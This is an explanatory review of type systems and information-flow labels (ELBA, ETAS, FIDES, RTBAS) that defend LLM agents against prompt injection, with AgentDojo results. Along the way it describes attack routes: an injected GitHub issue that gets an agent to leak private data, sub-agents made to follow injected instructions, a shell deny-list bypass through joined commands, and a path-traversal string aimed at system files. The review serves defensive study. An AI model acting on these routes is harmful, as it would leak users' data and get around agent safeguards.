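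Because the second call is inside a `BibIO` program, Haskell infers that its result must also be `BibIO ()`, so the sub-agent is under the same restrictions as its parent. The parent can tighten these restrictions, for example by requiring a plain `String`, which prevents the sub-agent from performing any input or output. The parent can't loosen them, because a sub-agent of type `IO ()` would fail the type check just as `writeFile` does.

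Zhou and colleagues prove a general version of this. Let $L$ be the host language, and let $L_{agent}$ be the same language with agent calls added. The traces of a program $e$ are the sequences of tool calls with observable side effects that it can produce. A property $P$ of such sets of traces belongs to a type $t$ if every program of that type has it:

$$\vdash_L e : t \;\Longrightarrow\; P(\mathrm{traces}(e))$$

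The theorem states that a type guarantees in $L_{agent}$ every property it guarantees in $L$. The proof replaces each agent call with an ordinary function in $L$ that queries the model, type-checks the answer and runs it. Generated code may contain further agent calls, so the proof uses induction on the nesting depth, which has a fixed limit. The resulting program in $L$ has the same type and traces as the original, so the property also holds for the original. The proof treats the model as an arbitrary function, so the theorem holds even if an attacker completely controls the model.

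ELBA's guarantees depend on the developer writing the whole application in Haskell, including its control flow and the logic for retrying failed calls. If a Python script passed the agent's output to a shell, the types would not govern that step. In the AgentDojo tests, ELBA had to connect to tools written in Python. In that setup, the types limit which tools the agent's code can call, but the developer has to trust the tools' Python code.

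The theorem also adds nothing to what the host language already enforces, so the agent's code should stay within Safe Haskell, the subset without functions that hide effects under a pure type. According to the *Safe Haskell* chapter of the GHC compiler's manual, the subset also excludes Template Haskell, which generates code during compilation and can access constructors that a module hides. An agent could otherwise use it to forge a `Trusted Bib`. Code in this subset may import only trusted modules. A module is trusted if the compiler has checked it or if its author has marked it `Trustworthy`, which the compiler accepts without checking. An optional setting requires whoever compiles the program to approve the packages that contain modules marked `Trustworthy`.

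According to GHC's documentation, Safe Haskell gives no protection during compilation, when a flag can make the compiler launch other programs. Source files set such flags at the top, but ELBA prompts the model for a single expression instead of a whole file, which should leave little room for this attack.

### File access through `Path` values

In the file library by Zhou and colleagues, the capability for a directory is a `Path` value, and code that uses it has the effect type `RIO`. Here `root` is the `Path` for a directory that the application chose, and the operator `//` narrows it to something inside that directory:

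```
do contents <- readRIO (root // "input.txt")
   writeRIO (root // "output.txt") contents
```

Passing a plain file name where a `Path` is expected fails the type check. But `root // "../../etc/passwd"` has the right type, and the compiler can't check where it leads. The `//` operator therefore works out the real location at run time, following any symbolic links, and rejects the path if it falls outside the directory.

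The function that opens a new root directory returns an `IO` type, so code that must have type `RIO` can't use it to open another directory. In TACIT's general-purpose library, by contrast, the agent's own code specifies which directory to access.

Coding agents such as Claude Code commonly restrict shell commands by matching them against a list of text patterns. Zhou and colleagues describe a bug from March 2026 in which Claude Code checked only the first of several joined commands against its list of forbidden ones. A short Python command can also open a forbidden file without matching any pattern. ELBA avoids both problems unless the developer gives the agent a function that runs shell commands.

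### Information-flow control with LIO

For policies about data, ELBA uses an existing Haskell library called LIO. *Flexible Dynamic Information Flow Control in Haskell* (Stefan, Russo and colleagues, 2011) presented the library. Programs that use LIO have their own effect type, called `DC` in ELBA. The type checker ensures that all their side effects go through LIO's functions, which check labels while the program runs.

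LIO keeps one label for the whole running computation, the current label $l_{cur}$. When the program reads data with label $l_d$, the current label rises to $l_{cur} \sqcup l_d$. The program may then write to a destination with label $l_e$ only if

$$l_{cur} \sqsubseteq l_e$$

An agent that starts with public, trusted data has the label $(L, T)$. Once it reads a page from the open web, its label becomes $(L, U)$, and LIO raises an error if the agent tries to write anywhere that accepts only trusted data.

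Zhou and colleagues use this for a low-watermark policy, under which a model that reads untrusted data drops to the privileges of the data's source. The label rises as trust falls because untrusted data is higher in the ordering of permitted flows. In *Flexible Dynamic Information Flow Control in the Presence of Exceptions*, Stefan, Russo and colleagues trace rising labels to the ADEPT-50 system of the late 1960s.

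Using one label for everything also stops leaks through branching, which simple taint tracking misses. To branch on a secret, an LIO program must first read it, which raises the label and prevents public output in both branches. The drawback is label creep, where restrictions accumulate, as they do in an agent loop, until the program can't do anything useful.

LIO's remedy is the function `toLabeled`, which runs part of a program separately and then restores the program's earlier label. It returns the result in a sealed wrapper that the rest of the program can pass on, but opening the wrapper raises the program's label. The program must choose the wrapper's label beforehand. Otherwise the inner part could read something more secret only when a secret bit is 1, and the outer part could learn the bit from the wrapper's label alone.

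Calling a sub-agent inside `toLabeled` resembles the dual-LLM pattern, except that the sub-agent can still use tools. In an example from Zhou and colleagues, an agent must send a direct message summarising an external email whose web address comes from untrusted data. The sub-agent fetches the email and drafts the message, and only its own label rises. The main agent then passes the sealed draft to a function that sends direct messages. Because the main agent chooses the recipient, the function checks that no untrusted data has influenced that agent before using a special privilege to unseal the draft. An attacker who wrote the email can influence the wording of the message but not who receives it.

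LIO can also limit how far a computation's label may rise. Its documentation calls this limit the clearance and suggests it for "need-to-know" policies. The clearance helps prevent leaks through timing, because code can't leak a secret it can't read.

Stefan and colleagues proved noninterference for LIO's core and checked much of the proof in Coq. The theorem doesn't cover leaks through timing or through whether a program finishes, although a separate version of LIO for concurrent programs handles the latter. The formal model also leaves out privileges. ELBA's function for sending messages relies on a privilege, so the theorem doesn't cover sending, and the developer has to make sure that step is correct.

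*IFC Inside* describes two mistakes in LIO, an established library. LIO originally restored the clearance incorrectly after an exception, and it always let errors in pure code reach the surrounding trusted code, so an attacker could have used them to crash the system. LIO's developers later adopted a simpler design.

### Results on AgentDojo's Slack tasks

Zhou and colleagues compared ELBA with CaMeL on AgentDojo's 21 Slack tasks, running each system with and without its information-flow policies. CaMeL writes its whole program before reading any data. Without policies, ELBA gives the Slack functions a plain `IO` type. The table shows how many tasks each system completed when there was no attack.

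| Model | ELBA | CaMeL | ELBA, no policies | CaMeL, no policies |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Opus 4.7 | 10 | 5 | 18 | 15 |
| Claude Opus 4.8 | 9 | 6 | 16 | 16 |
| GPT 5.4 | 10 | 5 | 16 | 17 |
| Claude Sonnet 5 | 8 | 4 | 14 | 13 |

With policies, ELBA completed nearly twice as many tasks as CaMeL. The comparison covers only 21 tasks, but ELBA also led in the 105 attack cases. With policies and the simplest attack wording, the 95% confidence interval for the difference is above zero for all four models. Without policies, ELBA's lead is smaller, and CaMeL did slightly better in several settings with GPT 5.4.

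Zhou and colleagues attribute CaMeL's lower utility to its separation of planning from data. That probably explains part of the gap, but the two systems also enforce different policies, and a more lenient policy blocks fewer tasks. ELBA took about three times as long to run as CaMeL, mainly because its agents query the model again after reading data. Type errors caused only 0.13 retries per run on average, and in all but 7 of 2,688 runs the model eventually produced code that passed the type check. Label violations are harder to handle because LIO detects them while the program is running, when earlier steps may already have had side effects.

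Every model resisted all 105 standard attacks in each of three wordings, even without policies, in both ELBA and CaMeL, so these attacks showed no difference between the systems. Policies are still needed because attackers can adapt. Zhou and colleagues point out that OpenAI's automated attacker, GPT-Red, consistently got past the defences of GPT-5.5.

The researchers therefore simulated the worst case. In ELBA, agents read all data through sub-agents, whose prompts contain a task followed by the data. The researchers changed ELBA so that whenever the data contained an AgentDojo attack, the sub-agent received only the data, as if it were the task. The sub-agent then carried out the attacker's instructions. They ran the 105 cases seven times with each model, for a total of 735 trials per model.

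| Model | Attacks that succeeded, no policies | Attacks that succeeded, policies | Tasks completed, no policies | Tasks completed, policies |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Opus 4.7 | 42.2% | 0% | 71.2% | 47.8% |
| Claude Opus 4.8 | 37.4% | 0% | 75.8% | 42.4% |
| GPT 5.4 | 15.5% | 0% | 75.9% | 46.0% |
| Claude Sonnet 5 | 26.5% | 0% | 67.2% | 40.0% |

The policies stopped all 735 attacks for each model. Each model completed between 494 and 558 of 735 tasks without the policies, and between 294 and 351 with them. These figures follow the rates in the paper's appendix. The main results table gives different counts for GPT 5.4, with 256 tasks completed without policies and 290 with them.

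AgentDojo's scoring counted 28 or 29 of the 2,940 runs with policies as successful attacks (the paper gives both numbers). In these runs the agent only opened a fixed web address, which the policies allow because the address reveals nothing. Zhou and colleagues reviewed the runs by hand and found no violation.

The policies account for most of the lost tasks. With them on, the models completed 38% to 48% of tasks when nobody attacked, about the same as in the simulated worst case. The low-watermark policy judges data by its source, not its content, so reading a harmless web page lowers an agent's trust level as much as reading a hostile one. After reading the page, the agent may not take a privileged action based on it. The policies also block web requests once the agent has read sensitive data, because the request could reveal something about that data.

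This policy interferes with tasks like inviting Dora to Slack with the address from her website, because it doesn't distinguish a legitimate invitation from an attack.

Zhou and colleagues reply that a defence with many false alarms is still useful if it never misses a violation of its policy. They cite an argument by Aashish Kolluri and colleagues that such a defence can safely reduce how often an agent asks its user for approval. Actions that pass the check go ahead automatically, and the user judges only the rest. This is a reasonable use of ELBA for someone who now approves every command by hand. But the experiments had no user to approve anything, so they don't show how many requests would remain or how many of the lost tasks would succeed with a user's approval.

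## ETAS: effect types that also fix the order of actions

An agent that needs a person's approval must get it before it acts. Effect types of the kind ELBA takes from Haskell can't express this, because they list the actions a piece of code may perform but not their order. A function that asks for approval and then changes a repository has the same effects as one that changes the repository and then asks. *ETAS* (Tan, Wang and colleagues, 2026) presents a programming language for agents, with types that also record the order of actions.

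In TACIT and ELBA, the model writes code and a compiler checks it. A developer normally writes an ETAS program, and querying the model is one of the program's actions. The model's proposed tool calls return to the program as data, and the program checks their names and arguments before it requests anything.

### A patch that needs approval

The main example is an agent that reviews patches, which are proposed changes to a code repository. In simplified form, the function that applies a patch looks like this:

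```
spec ApprovedApply = Approval.request >> Repo.apply;

flow apply(p: Patch) -> unit
  ![Approval.request, Repo.apply] ~ ApprovedApply
{
  if perform Approval.request(p) {
    perform Repo.apply(p);
  }
}
```

The keyword `perform` requests an action. `Approval.request` asks a person for approval and returns true or false, and `Repo.apply` writes the patch to the repository. Every function has an effect row, written after the exclamation mark, which lists the effects it may have. An earlier version of the paper includes a report-writing agent. The function that saves a report may write only to files under `reports/`, and the agent that drafts the report may search the web and read earlier reports but not write anything.

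The first line defines a trace specification, a rule about the order of requests. The operator `>>` requires at least one approval request before any write. The `~` attaches the rule to the function.

A programmer could break the rule by deleting the approval request or moving it below the write. Neither edit changes the function's argument or result type. Both versions also stay within the declared row, because a row is an upper bound on effects and doesn't specify their order. A compiler that checked only ordinary types and rows would accept both versions, but the ETAS compiler rejects them.

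ELBA could also enforce this order, in the same way that it keeps invented papers out of the bibliography. The function that applies patches would accept only an `Approved Patch`, and only the approval function could produce one. This would also tie each approval to a particular patch. But the developer would have to design the functions around the rule, whereas in ETAS the rule is separate and can cover existing actions.

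### What a dry run hides

Developers often want to test an agent without letting it change anything. Effect handlers, the surrounding code that determines what an operation does, make this easy:

```
let DryRun = handler {
  Repo.apply(p) => { resume; }
};
handle apply(patch) with DryRun
```

When the program requests `Repo.apply`, the handler intercepts the request, leaves the repository unchanged and resumes the program as if the write had happened. A handler can instead use `finish` to end the whole block early with its own result.

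In most languages with handlers, intercepting an effect also removes it from the type. Bauer and Pretnar (2013), in *An Effect System for Algebraic Effects and Handlers*, treat this as an important feature. Code that reads and updates a variable counts as pure once a handler intercepts those operations. *Abstracting Effect Systems for Algebraic Effect Handlers* (2024) describes the same behaviour for rows, which lose an effect when a handler intercepts it. This makes sense if a type only has to list the effects that can still reach callers. With an agent, though, the type would no longer show an attempted write, so a test under `DryRun` would no longer check whether approval came first.

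ETAS therefore computes two things for each piece of code. The escaping row $\varepsilon$ contains the effects that may still reach the outside world. The request summary $A$ describes the possible sequences of requests, including those that a handler intercepts. A `perform` adds its action to both. If one piece of code runs after another, the compiler takes the union of their rows but puts their summaries in order:

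$$\varepsilon = \varepsilon_1 \cup \varepsilon_2, \qquad A = A_1 ; A_2$$

For an `if`, the summary is $A_1 \sqcup A_2$, which means either branch. Writing $g$ for an approval request, $w$ for a write and $1$ for no request at all, the function above has

$$\varepsilon = \{g, w\}, \qquad A = g ; (1 \sqcup w)$$

It always asks, and then either stops or writes. A handler for a set of actions $H$ changes the two as follows:

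$$\varepsilon' = (\varepsilon \setminus H) \cup \varepsilon_h, \qquad A' = \mathrm{pref}(A \parallel A_h^{\ast})$$

Here $\varepsilon_h$ and $A_h$ belong to the handler's own code. The symbol $\parallel$ interleaves two sequences, and the star allows the handler to run any number of times. Because the handler may end the block early, $\mathrm{pref}$ adds every unfinished sequence. `DryRun` makes no requests itself, so the row shrinks to $\{g\}$, but the summary still contains the write.

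The rule therefore applies to dry runs too. A reviewer might want to see a dry run of the patch before approving it, but a dry-run write before the approval request violates `ApprovedApply`. A developer who wanted to allow such dry runs would need a separate action for them.

Recording order in types is older than ETAS. *A HAT Trick* (2024) cites a 2004 system by Christian Skalka and Scott Smith that describes the possible histories of a program's events, with security rules in mind. *When Types Intersect and Effects Get Handled* (Catozi, Dal Lago and Sekiyama, 2026) presents types that are more precise than those of ETAS. They record which operation a program performs first and every way in which a handler may continue it. A program has such a type exactly when it terminates, so no algorithm can find these types for all programs. A compiler can always check the much coarser ETAS summaries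 against a rule.

### Proving the rule or monitoring it

The compiler translates `ApprovedApply` into an expression for all the permitted sequences:

$$P = 1 \sqcup g ; (g \sqcup w)^{\ast}$$

A run may request nothing, or it may begin with an approval request and continue with any mix of approvals and writes. Since $P$ mentions no other actions, it forbids them, so the rule is also a list of what the function may request. To prove that the function obeys it, the compiler must show that every sequence in the summary, finished or not, is in $P$:

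$$\mathrm{Pref}(\mathcal{L}(A)) \subseteq \mathcal{L}(P)$$

The original function's possible sequences are the empty one, $g$, and $g$ followed by $w$, all in $P$. If the programmer moves the approval below the write, the sequences begin with $w$, which is not in $P$.

The compiler does this comparison with a finite-state machine, the same kind of monitor as Schneider's security automaton. For this rule it has three states:

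| State | After an approval request | After a write request |
|---|---|---|
| No approval requested | Approval requested | Violation |
| Approval requested | Approval requested | Approval requested |
| Violation | Violation | Violation |

The compiler works out every state in which the function could end. If the violation state isn't among them, the compiler has proved that the program follows the rule, and the program doesn't need the monitor. If the violation state is the only possibility, the compiler rejects the program. If the function could end in the violation state or in another state, the program may run, but only with the monitor attached.

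A function that asks first in one branch and writes first in the other falls into the uncertain group. Under the paper's rules it compiles, even though the branch that writes first is clearly wrong. If a run takes that branch, the monitor stops it before the write, but the developer may not notice the bug until then.

During a run, every request first goes to the active monitors. If they allow it, the request goes to a handler that covers the action or, if there is none, to the host, the software that carries out actions. The host proceeds only if the action is in the declared row and a separate permission check accepts the actual arguments. A permanent log records whether each request ended in a handler, an executed action or a refusal.

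`ApprovedApply` is weaker than its name suggests, because it requires the program to request approval but doesn't require the person to give it. If a programmer deleted the `if` and kept both requests, the function would write the patch whatever the person answered, and its summary, $g;w$, would still satisfy the rule. One approval followed by writes of ten different patches would satisfy it too. Tan and colleagues rely on the `if` to check the person's answer and on the host's permission check to establish consent to a particular patch. The order rule doesn't check either piece of code, so it can't guarantee that the reviewer agreed to the patch being written, which is what matters most to them.

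Agent-C, a system in *Enforcing Temporal Constraints for LLM Agents* (2025), has rules that compare the arguments of different calls. One rule lets an agent read a file only after an earlier call has opened it. Another requires the agent to close every file it opens. ETAS can't enforce the second rule because its monitors enforce only safety properties.

### What the theorems cover

Two of the theorems are standard for typed languages. Preservation means each step of a well-typed program either keeps the program's result type or ends in an error. Progress means the program never reaches a state for which the language has no rule.

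The others concern actions. If $t$ is the log of a run, $\mathrm{commits}(t)$ the actions that the host executed, and $\mathrm{reqs}(t)$ the sequence of requests that the monitors admitted, then

$$\mathrm{commits}(t) \subseteq \varepsilon, \qquad \mathrm{reqs}(t) \in \mathcal{L}(P)$$

The first part, effect coverage, means that the program performs no effects outside the escaping row. The second, trace safety, holds whether the compiler proved the rule or left a monitor to check it. A further theorem shows that handlers cannot delete a request from the log or let an action bypass the usual checks.

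All of this holds for any model reply of the expected type, but it depends on the host. Tan and colleagues assume complete mediation, meaning that every external action goes through the ETAS runtime. They also assume that each permitted host operation either returns a result of the declared type or fails. The trusted base therefore includes the compiler, the interpreter, the host services, the permission check and whoever writes the rules. The ETAS proofs are on paper, whereas Lean has checked the core theorems behind TACIT's type system.

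Models can also revise ETAS programs. In one set of experiments, they revised the agents' prompts and processing code over five rounds, using feedback from earlier runs. Each revision had to compile against fixed types, effect limits and order rules before it could run, and the revised code could not loosen them. Accuracy on 256 financial questions rose from 69.9% to 78.9%. This result concerns only task performance, but it suggests that fixed rules leave room for useful changes.

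### Small tests with scripted models

Tan and colleagues wrote a coding agent, Nomo, in ETAS and tested enforcement on the 1,417 lines that decide which files to read or search. They ran ten scenarios in which handlers supplied prepared model replies and tool results. Four finished normally and six stopped where they should have. The handlers dealt correctly with all 19 requests. The compiler also rejected two faulty versions of the code, one with the wrong return type and one with an undeclared effect.

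The researchers tested the compiler on six separate programs involving approvals and writes. It accepted the correct program and its dry-run version. It rejected the other four: the two edits described above, a program in which a handler intercepted a forbidden write, and one with a write missing from the declared row. The researchers also wrote a Python model of the order rules and compared its monitors with a direct check on every sequence of up to six actions. All 419,712 comparisons agreed. This supports the theory but doesn't test the compiler's Rust code.

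Tan and colleagues report no tests with adversarial models, and none of these enforcement tests used a live model. The tests are closer to a compiler's regression tests than to the attack trials on TACIT and ELBA, and they do not show how many legitimate tasks the rules would block.

*Declarative Skills for AI Agents in Knowledge-Grounded Tool-Use Workflows* (2026) offers some evidence that an order rule need not lower an agent's success rate much. Its agent had to complete a verification step before any tool call that writes data. A simple check intercepted early writes and told the model to verify first. With DeepSeek-V4-Pro, none of 467 write calls went through before verification, compared with 4.3% without the check. The agent's success rate was 49.0% with the check and 46.2% without it, a difference within the noise. The check required no new language or proof. For a single rule of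 this kind, ETAS mainly adds a way for a developer to find the mistake before the agent runs.

The paper's largest numbers are for running time and input tokens. The compiler can identify code that has no effects and reorganise it safely, which cut running time by 23.2% on 26 synthetic workflows. That figure excludes time spent waiting for models and networks, so the saving in a real agent would probably be much smaller. Trimming unneeded history, tool descriptions, data fields and source code from prompts cut input tokens by 67.8% on 12 workflows with MiniMax-M3.1-Flash. These results don't show whether the order rules stop bad actions.

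### Bastion: specifications richer than order

A 2024 proposal called Bastion would attach much stronger conditions to an agent's actions. Omar, Ferris and Madhavapeddy, in *Modularizing Reasoning about AI Capabilities via Abstract Dijkstra Monads*, outlined it for a workshop at ICFP (2024), a conference on functional programming. An agent would write its commands as small programs in F⋆, a language that combines programming with proof. As with ELBA's `BibIO`, the agent could combine the commands that a policy provides but could not make new ones:

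```
readfile  : path -> Cmd string
writefile : path -> string -> Cmd ()
```

The policy would set which directories each agent can read and which it can write to for each task. A second AI would look for access that the task doesn't need, and it could remove permissions but not add them.

To prove that the commands respect the policy, Bastion would use Dijkstra monads. Ahman, Hriţcu and colleagues (2017), in *Dijkstra Monads for Free*, explain these as a way to specify code with effects through weakest preconditions. The weakest precondition of a command is the least that must be true beforehand for a desired result $Q$ to hold afterwards. Maillard, Ahman and colleagues (2019) later extended the method to arbitrary effects of the kind that monads can describe. For the patch example, a specification might be

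$$\mathrm{wp}(\mathrm{apply}(p), Q)(s) = \mathrm{approved}(p, s) \land Q(s')$$

where $s$ is the state before the write and $s'$ the state after it. The write is allowed only if the person has approved patch $p$ itself, which `ApprovedApply` cannot require.

Specifications like this can contain almost any logical statement. Omar and colleagues want to use them for information flow and eventually for proving causal claims, such as that an environmental intervention will probably respect water rights. In some cases the agent would have to supply the proof before acting. Someone must write the specifications and find the proofs, whereas ETAS compares its finite-state rules automatically. Causal proofs would also need an accurate model of the relevant part of the world, and Omar and colleagues expect the policies to take a "large-scale, collaborative effort". Their proposal describes a planned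 prototype and has no experimental results.

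## FIDES: trust and secrecy labels on what an agent reads

TACIT, ELBA and ETAS require the model or a developer to write the agent's actions in a programming language. FIDES, which Costa and colleagues at Microsoft presented in 2025, works with an ordinary agent loop, where the model requests one tool call at a time and writes no code. It labels everything the agent reads, then allows or blocks each tool call based on the labels of the data that influenced it.

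### How the loop checks a call

In its simplest form, the method has five steps:

1. The conversation begins with the user's request, which counts as public and trusted. The program around the model keeps one label for the whole conversation, the context label $\ell$.
2. The program sends the conversation to the model and gives the reply the context label, because nobody can tell which parts of the conversation influenced it.
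3. If the reply requests a tool call, the choice of tool and every argument inherit that label. The program checks the call against a policy and runs the tool only if the call passes.
4. The result gets the join of the labels of the call, its arguments and any data the tool read.
5. The program adds the result to the conversation and replaces $\ell$ with $\ell \sqcup \ell_r$, where $\ell_r$ is the result's label. Then it returns to step 2.

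In the paper's formal model, a failed check ends the run, but in the tests the program reported the refusal to the language model so that the agent could try something else. The check is done by ordinary code that compares labels, without involving the language model.

Costa and colleagues describe two basic policies. Write $\ell_f$ for the label of the decision to call a tool, and $\ell_1, \ldots, \ell_n$ for the labels of its arguments. The integrity policy covers tools with serious consequences, such as moving money. It permits a call only if everything behind it is trusted:

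$$\ell_f \sqcup \ell_1 \sqcup \dots \sqcup \ell_n = (\_, T)$$

The blank means that the data may be public or secret. The confidentiality policy covers tools that send data to someone. If $S$ is the set of people who may read the data and $R$ is the set who would receive it, the policy permits the call only if

$$R \subseteq S$$

An attacker's text could still cause the agent to send a message that meets the confidentiality policy, but the message couldn't reveal anything its recipients weren't allowed to know.

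An application can require a call to satisfy both policies or either one. If either is enough, the agent may send private data to new people as long as no untrusted data influenced the call, because the user is then assumed to have wanted this. This rule is called robust declassification. In the AgentDojo tests, Costa and colleagues accepted either policy for emails and Slack messages. They required the integrity policy for payments, bookings and deletions, and both policies for adding people to a calendar event. Their confidentiality policy also blocked messages with untrusted links, because a link can leak data when software opens it.

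### Label creep and how FIDES limits it

Label creep is severe in this simple loop, as it can be in LIO. Once the agent reads one untrusted email, even a harmless and unrelated one, it can no longer pay a bill or book a hotel. With the checks, a basic GPT-4o agent completed 20% of Slack tasks, down from 93.3%.

When a tool result would raise the context label, FIDES stores it in a variable and shows the planning model only the variable's name, so the label stays the same. FIDES does this separately for each field. If an email has a trusted sender and an untrusted body, the model sees the sender but only a name such as `#read_emails_0.body` in place of the body.

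The model can use that name in a later tool call, and FIDES fills in the contents and their label before the check. To forward an email to Slack, the agent calls `send_message` with the recipient the user chose and the variable as the message. The recipient and the decision to send are then trusted, and only the message is untrusted.

If the user wants a summary of the email, FIDES gives the variable to a quarantined model, as in the dual-LLM pattern, and stores the answer in a new variable.

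Sometimes the planning model's next step depends on the data in a variable. The model can open the variable, which adds the contents to the conversation and raises the context label. It can also send the quarantined model a query with a small, fixed set of possible answers. Suppose the user wants a calendar event if one of the latest three emails requests a meeting. The quarantined model returns yes or no, and the planning model reads only that. If the answer is yes, a second query extracts the date and participants into a variable.

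FIDES includes the answer's type in its label and orders types by how much information they can carry:

$$\text{bool} \sqsubseteq \text{enum} \sqsubseteq \text{string}$$

A `bool` is a yes or no, and an `enum` is a choice from a fixed list. A policy can let the agent act on an untrusted yes or no but not on untrusted text, because a yes or no can't contain an instruction to forward the mailbox. The attacker can still choose the answer and thereby decide whether the agent creates an event. The labels also don't track how much information accumulates. The join of two `bool` labels is still `bool`, although two answers carry twice as much information as one.

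Costa and colleagues left the typed answers out of their tests because most AgentDojo tasks don't need them. In *The LLMbda Calculus*, Garby, Gordon and Sands (2026) object that relaxations of this kind make it hard to tell an intended release from a leak.

The tested policies had another gap. The integrity policy above covers a call's arguments, but the version used in the tests checked only $\ell_f$. If the user asks the agent to pay the December bill, the quarantined model can extract the account number from the untrusted bill, and the policy allows the payment. Anyone able to edit the bill could redirect the money. Checking the arguments as well would prevent this, but then the agent couldn't pay the bill unless the user endorsed it.

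### Tasks that depend on the data

How well hiding works depends on the task. Costa and colleagues call a task data-independent if one sequence of tool calls and one final answer would solve it whatever the data contains. Let $D$ be the set of possible starting states for a task $t$, and let $[\![t]\!](d)$ be the set of action sequences that solve it from state $d$. The task is data-independent if

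$$\bigcap_{d \in D} [\![t]\!](d) \neq \varnothing$$

Forwarding an email is data-independent, since the same calls work for any email. Creating an event only if an email asks for one is data-dependent, like the to-do request that the dual-LLM pattern couldn't handle.

The researchers classify about 43% of AgentDojo's Slack tasks and 44% of its banking tasks as data-dependent, compared with 5% of workspace tasks and 10% of travel tasks. This probably helps explain why CaMeL, which plans before it reads any data, did poorly on Slack in the ELBA comparison.

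### RTBAS: tracking only what the model used

Labels also spread because FIDES assumes that a reply depends on the whole conversation. *RTBAS* (Zhong, Chen and colleagues, 2025) instead uses a screener before each step to try to identify the parts of the conversation that the next action needs. It gives the action the join of those parts' labels and masks every part of the conversation that this label doesn't cover, so the agent's model sees only the rest.

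Suppose a user asks about hotel reviews and then asks the agent to pay a friend. The screener should find that the payment doesn't need the reviews, so RTBAS masks them and the payment goes ahead as trusted. If the screener wrongly marks the reviews as needed, the user gets an unnecessary request for confirmation. If it misses something the payment does need, RTBAS may mask that and the task may fail. Either way, the reviews can't trigger a payment without the user's confirmation.

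Zhong and colleagues are nearly right to conclude that a screener's mistakes can't compromise security. However, the screener reads the whole conversation, so hostile text can influence which parts it marks. An attacker could use this to decide whether the agent sees certain data or the user gets a confirmation request. LIO closes a similar gap by making the program choose a label before it reads the data.

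Zhong and colleagues built two screeners. One is a second language model, and the other is a small neural network that uses attention scores, which estimate how strongly each part of the input influenced a draft reply. With either screener, RTBAS stopped every attack that violated the policy on AgentDojo with GPT-4o. RTBAS didn't track one injection because the text containing it carried the user's own trusted label.

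Without attacks, utility fell by 10% with the language-model screener and 7.4% with the attention screener. On the Slack tasks, utility dropped to 22% and 33%, respectively. The banking tasks took about twice as long and cost about twice as much as without a defence. In 37 further test cases about private data, the language-model screener caused unnecessary confirmation requests 8% of the time, compared with 30% for an agent that asks before every call.

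*APPA* (2026) handles label creep differently. It keeps the ordinary single-agent loop and opens an isolated branch when the agent needs one, so the developer doesn't have to split the agent permanently into two models.

### Explicit secrecy

Costa and colleagues consider noninterference too strict for agents. In effect, it would forbid any publicly visible action once the agent has read a secret. They aim for explicit secrecy, which is meant to rule out direct copying of secrets. Take one run of the agent, and let $g$ be the combined effect of its steps on the stored data. Two states are low-equivalent, written $d_1 =_L d_2$, if their public data is the same. Explicit secrecy requires that

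$$d_1 =_L d_2 \;\Longrightarrow\; g(d_1) =_L g(d_2)$$

If the secrets had been different and the agent had taken the same steps, an observer would have seen the same public data.

Explicit secrecy doesn't cover what an observer can learn from which steps the agent takes. Suppose an agent posts "Meeting cancelled" in a public channel only if a confidential report shows a loss. The message contains nothing from the report, but anyone who knows the rule learns about the loss. Explicit secrecy also doesn't cover leaks through timing or the size of network packets.

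The formal definition seems weaker than the researchers intended. It treats the conversation as part of the program, so once a tool has returned a secret, that secret is a constant in every later step. If the agent copied the secret into a public message, $g$ would produce the same message from either state, and the run would satisfy the definition. FIDES's confidentiality policy would still block the message if the data had the right label, so the fault appears to be in the definition rather than the system.

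### AgentDojo results from 2025

Costa and colleagues tested security with GPT-4o against an attacker who knows the names of the agent's tools. They counted 152 successful attacks against a basic agent and 21 against FIDES when policy checks were off, and none against either when the checks were on.

AgentDojo's scoring still counted three successful attacks against FIDES with checks, all on Slack. Such cases arose because AgentDojo counted some invitations as successful attacks even though the policy had blocked them, and because the policy deliberately allows some actions, such as sending a Slack message that has no link and reveals nothing new to its readers. The FIDES paper also excludes attacks that only change the agent's answer, for example by adding praise for a hotel. TACIT doesn't cover these attacks either.

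The labels suited the benchmark unusually well because the researchers marked a field as untrusted if any AgentDojo attack placed text there. Someone deploying an agent has no list of attacks to work from and has to guess where they might come from.

They tested utility with GPT-4o and OpenAI's reasoning model o1. The table shows the share of tasks each agent completed when it was not under attack, averaged over the four domains.

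| | GPT-4o | o1 |
|---|---|---|
| Basic agent, no checks | 84.3% | 84.0% |
| FIDES, no checks | 60.6% | 77.6% |
| Basic agent, checks | 41.9% | 44.4% |
| FIDES, checks | 50.0% | 60.8% |

With checks on for both agents, FIDES completed 8 percentage points more tasks than the basic agent with GPT-4o and 16 points more with o1. The 6.3% utility loss given in the paper's summary compares the two agents with o1 and checks off, so it measures how much the variables confuse the model. The same gap was 23.7 points with GPT-4o. A better measure of the utility lost to protection is the gap between the basic agent with checks off and FIDES with checks on, which is about 23 points with o1.

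Many of the lost tasks are ones the policy is supposed to block, such as reading a file and following its instructions to make a payment. In others, the model mixed up variable names or read data it didn't need. The scores also include some lucky guesses. In one banking task, the user wants a new password if a transaction looks suspicious. The agent changed the password because the amount was large, without reading the untrusted description, and AgentDojo marked this as correct.

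### Prototypes in Microsoft and GitHub tools

Microsoft has since added FIDES to Agent Framework, its toolkit for building agents. Microsoft's *Stop prompt injection from hijacking your agent* (2026) announced the release in May, and the documentation still describes the feature as experimental. This version supports variables and a quarantined model. When a call violates a policy, the developer can have the program block it or ask the user.

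Labels are useful only if they travel with the data from the tool to the agent. The Model Context Protocol (MCP), which TACIT also uses, has metadata fields that can hold them. Microsoft's *Information-flow control* describes prototypes in which a tool server attaches labels to its results, and an agent's software sends labels back with each call. A server can also publish a policy for each tool. Software that doesn't know about the labels can still use the same server.

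GitHub's MCP server can now add such labels. It marks files and issues from public repositories as public and untrusted, and those from private repositories as private and trusted. The labels address an attack that researchers demonstrated in about 2025. An attacker opens an issue in a public repository that asks for information from a private one. An agent with access to both reads the issue, fetches the private data and posts it in a public comment. With labels, the agent's context is untrusted and private once it has read the issue and the private data, so the policy stops it from posting publicly.

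These labels are coarse. A private repository may contain outside text, such as a customer's bug report that an employee pasted into an issue, and the server would mark that text as trusted.

Microsoft gives another example without an attacker. Alex asks an agent to answer the unanswered emails in an inbox. Priya has sent Alex a preview of the quarterly sales, and Marco, who isn't allowed to see the figures yet, has also written. Once the agent has read both emails, anything it writes has the readers

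$$\{\text{Alex}, \text{Priya}\} \cap \{\text{Alex}, \text{Marco}\} = \{\text{Alex}\}$$

Marco isn't in this set, so the agent can't reply to him without asking Alex. If Priya had copied Marco in, the intersection would be {Alex, Marco} and the agent could send the reply. As things stand, the same calculation stops the agent from sending Marco even a reply about lunch without asking Alex.

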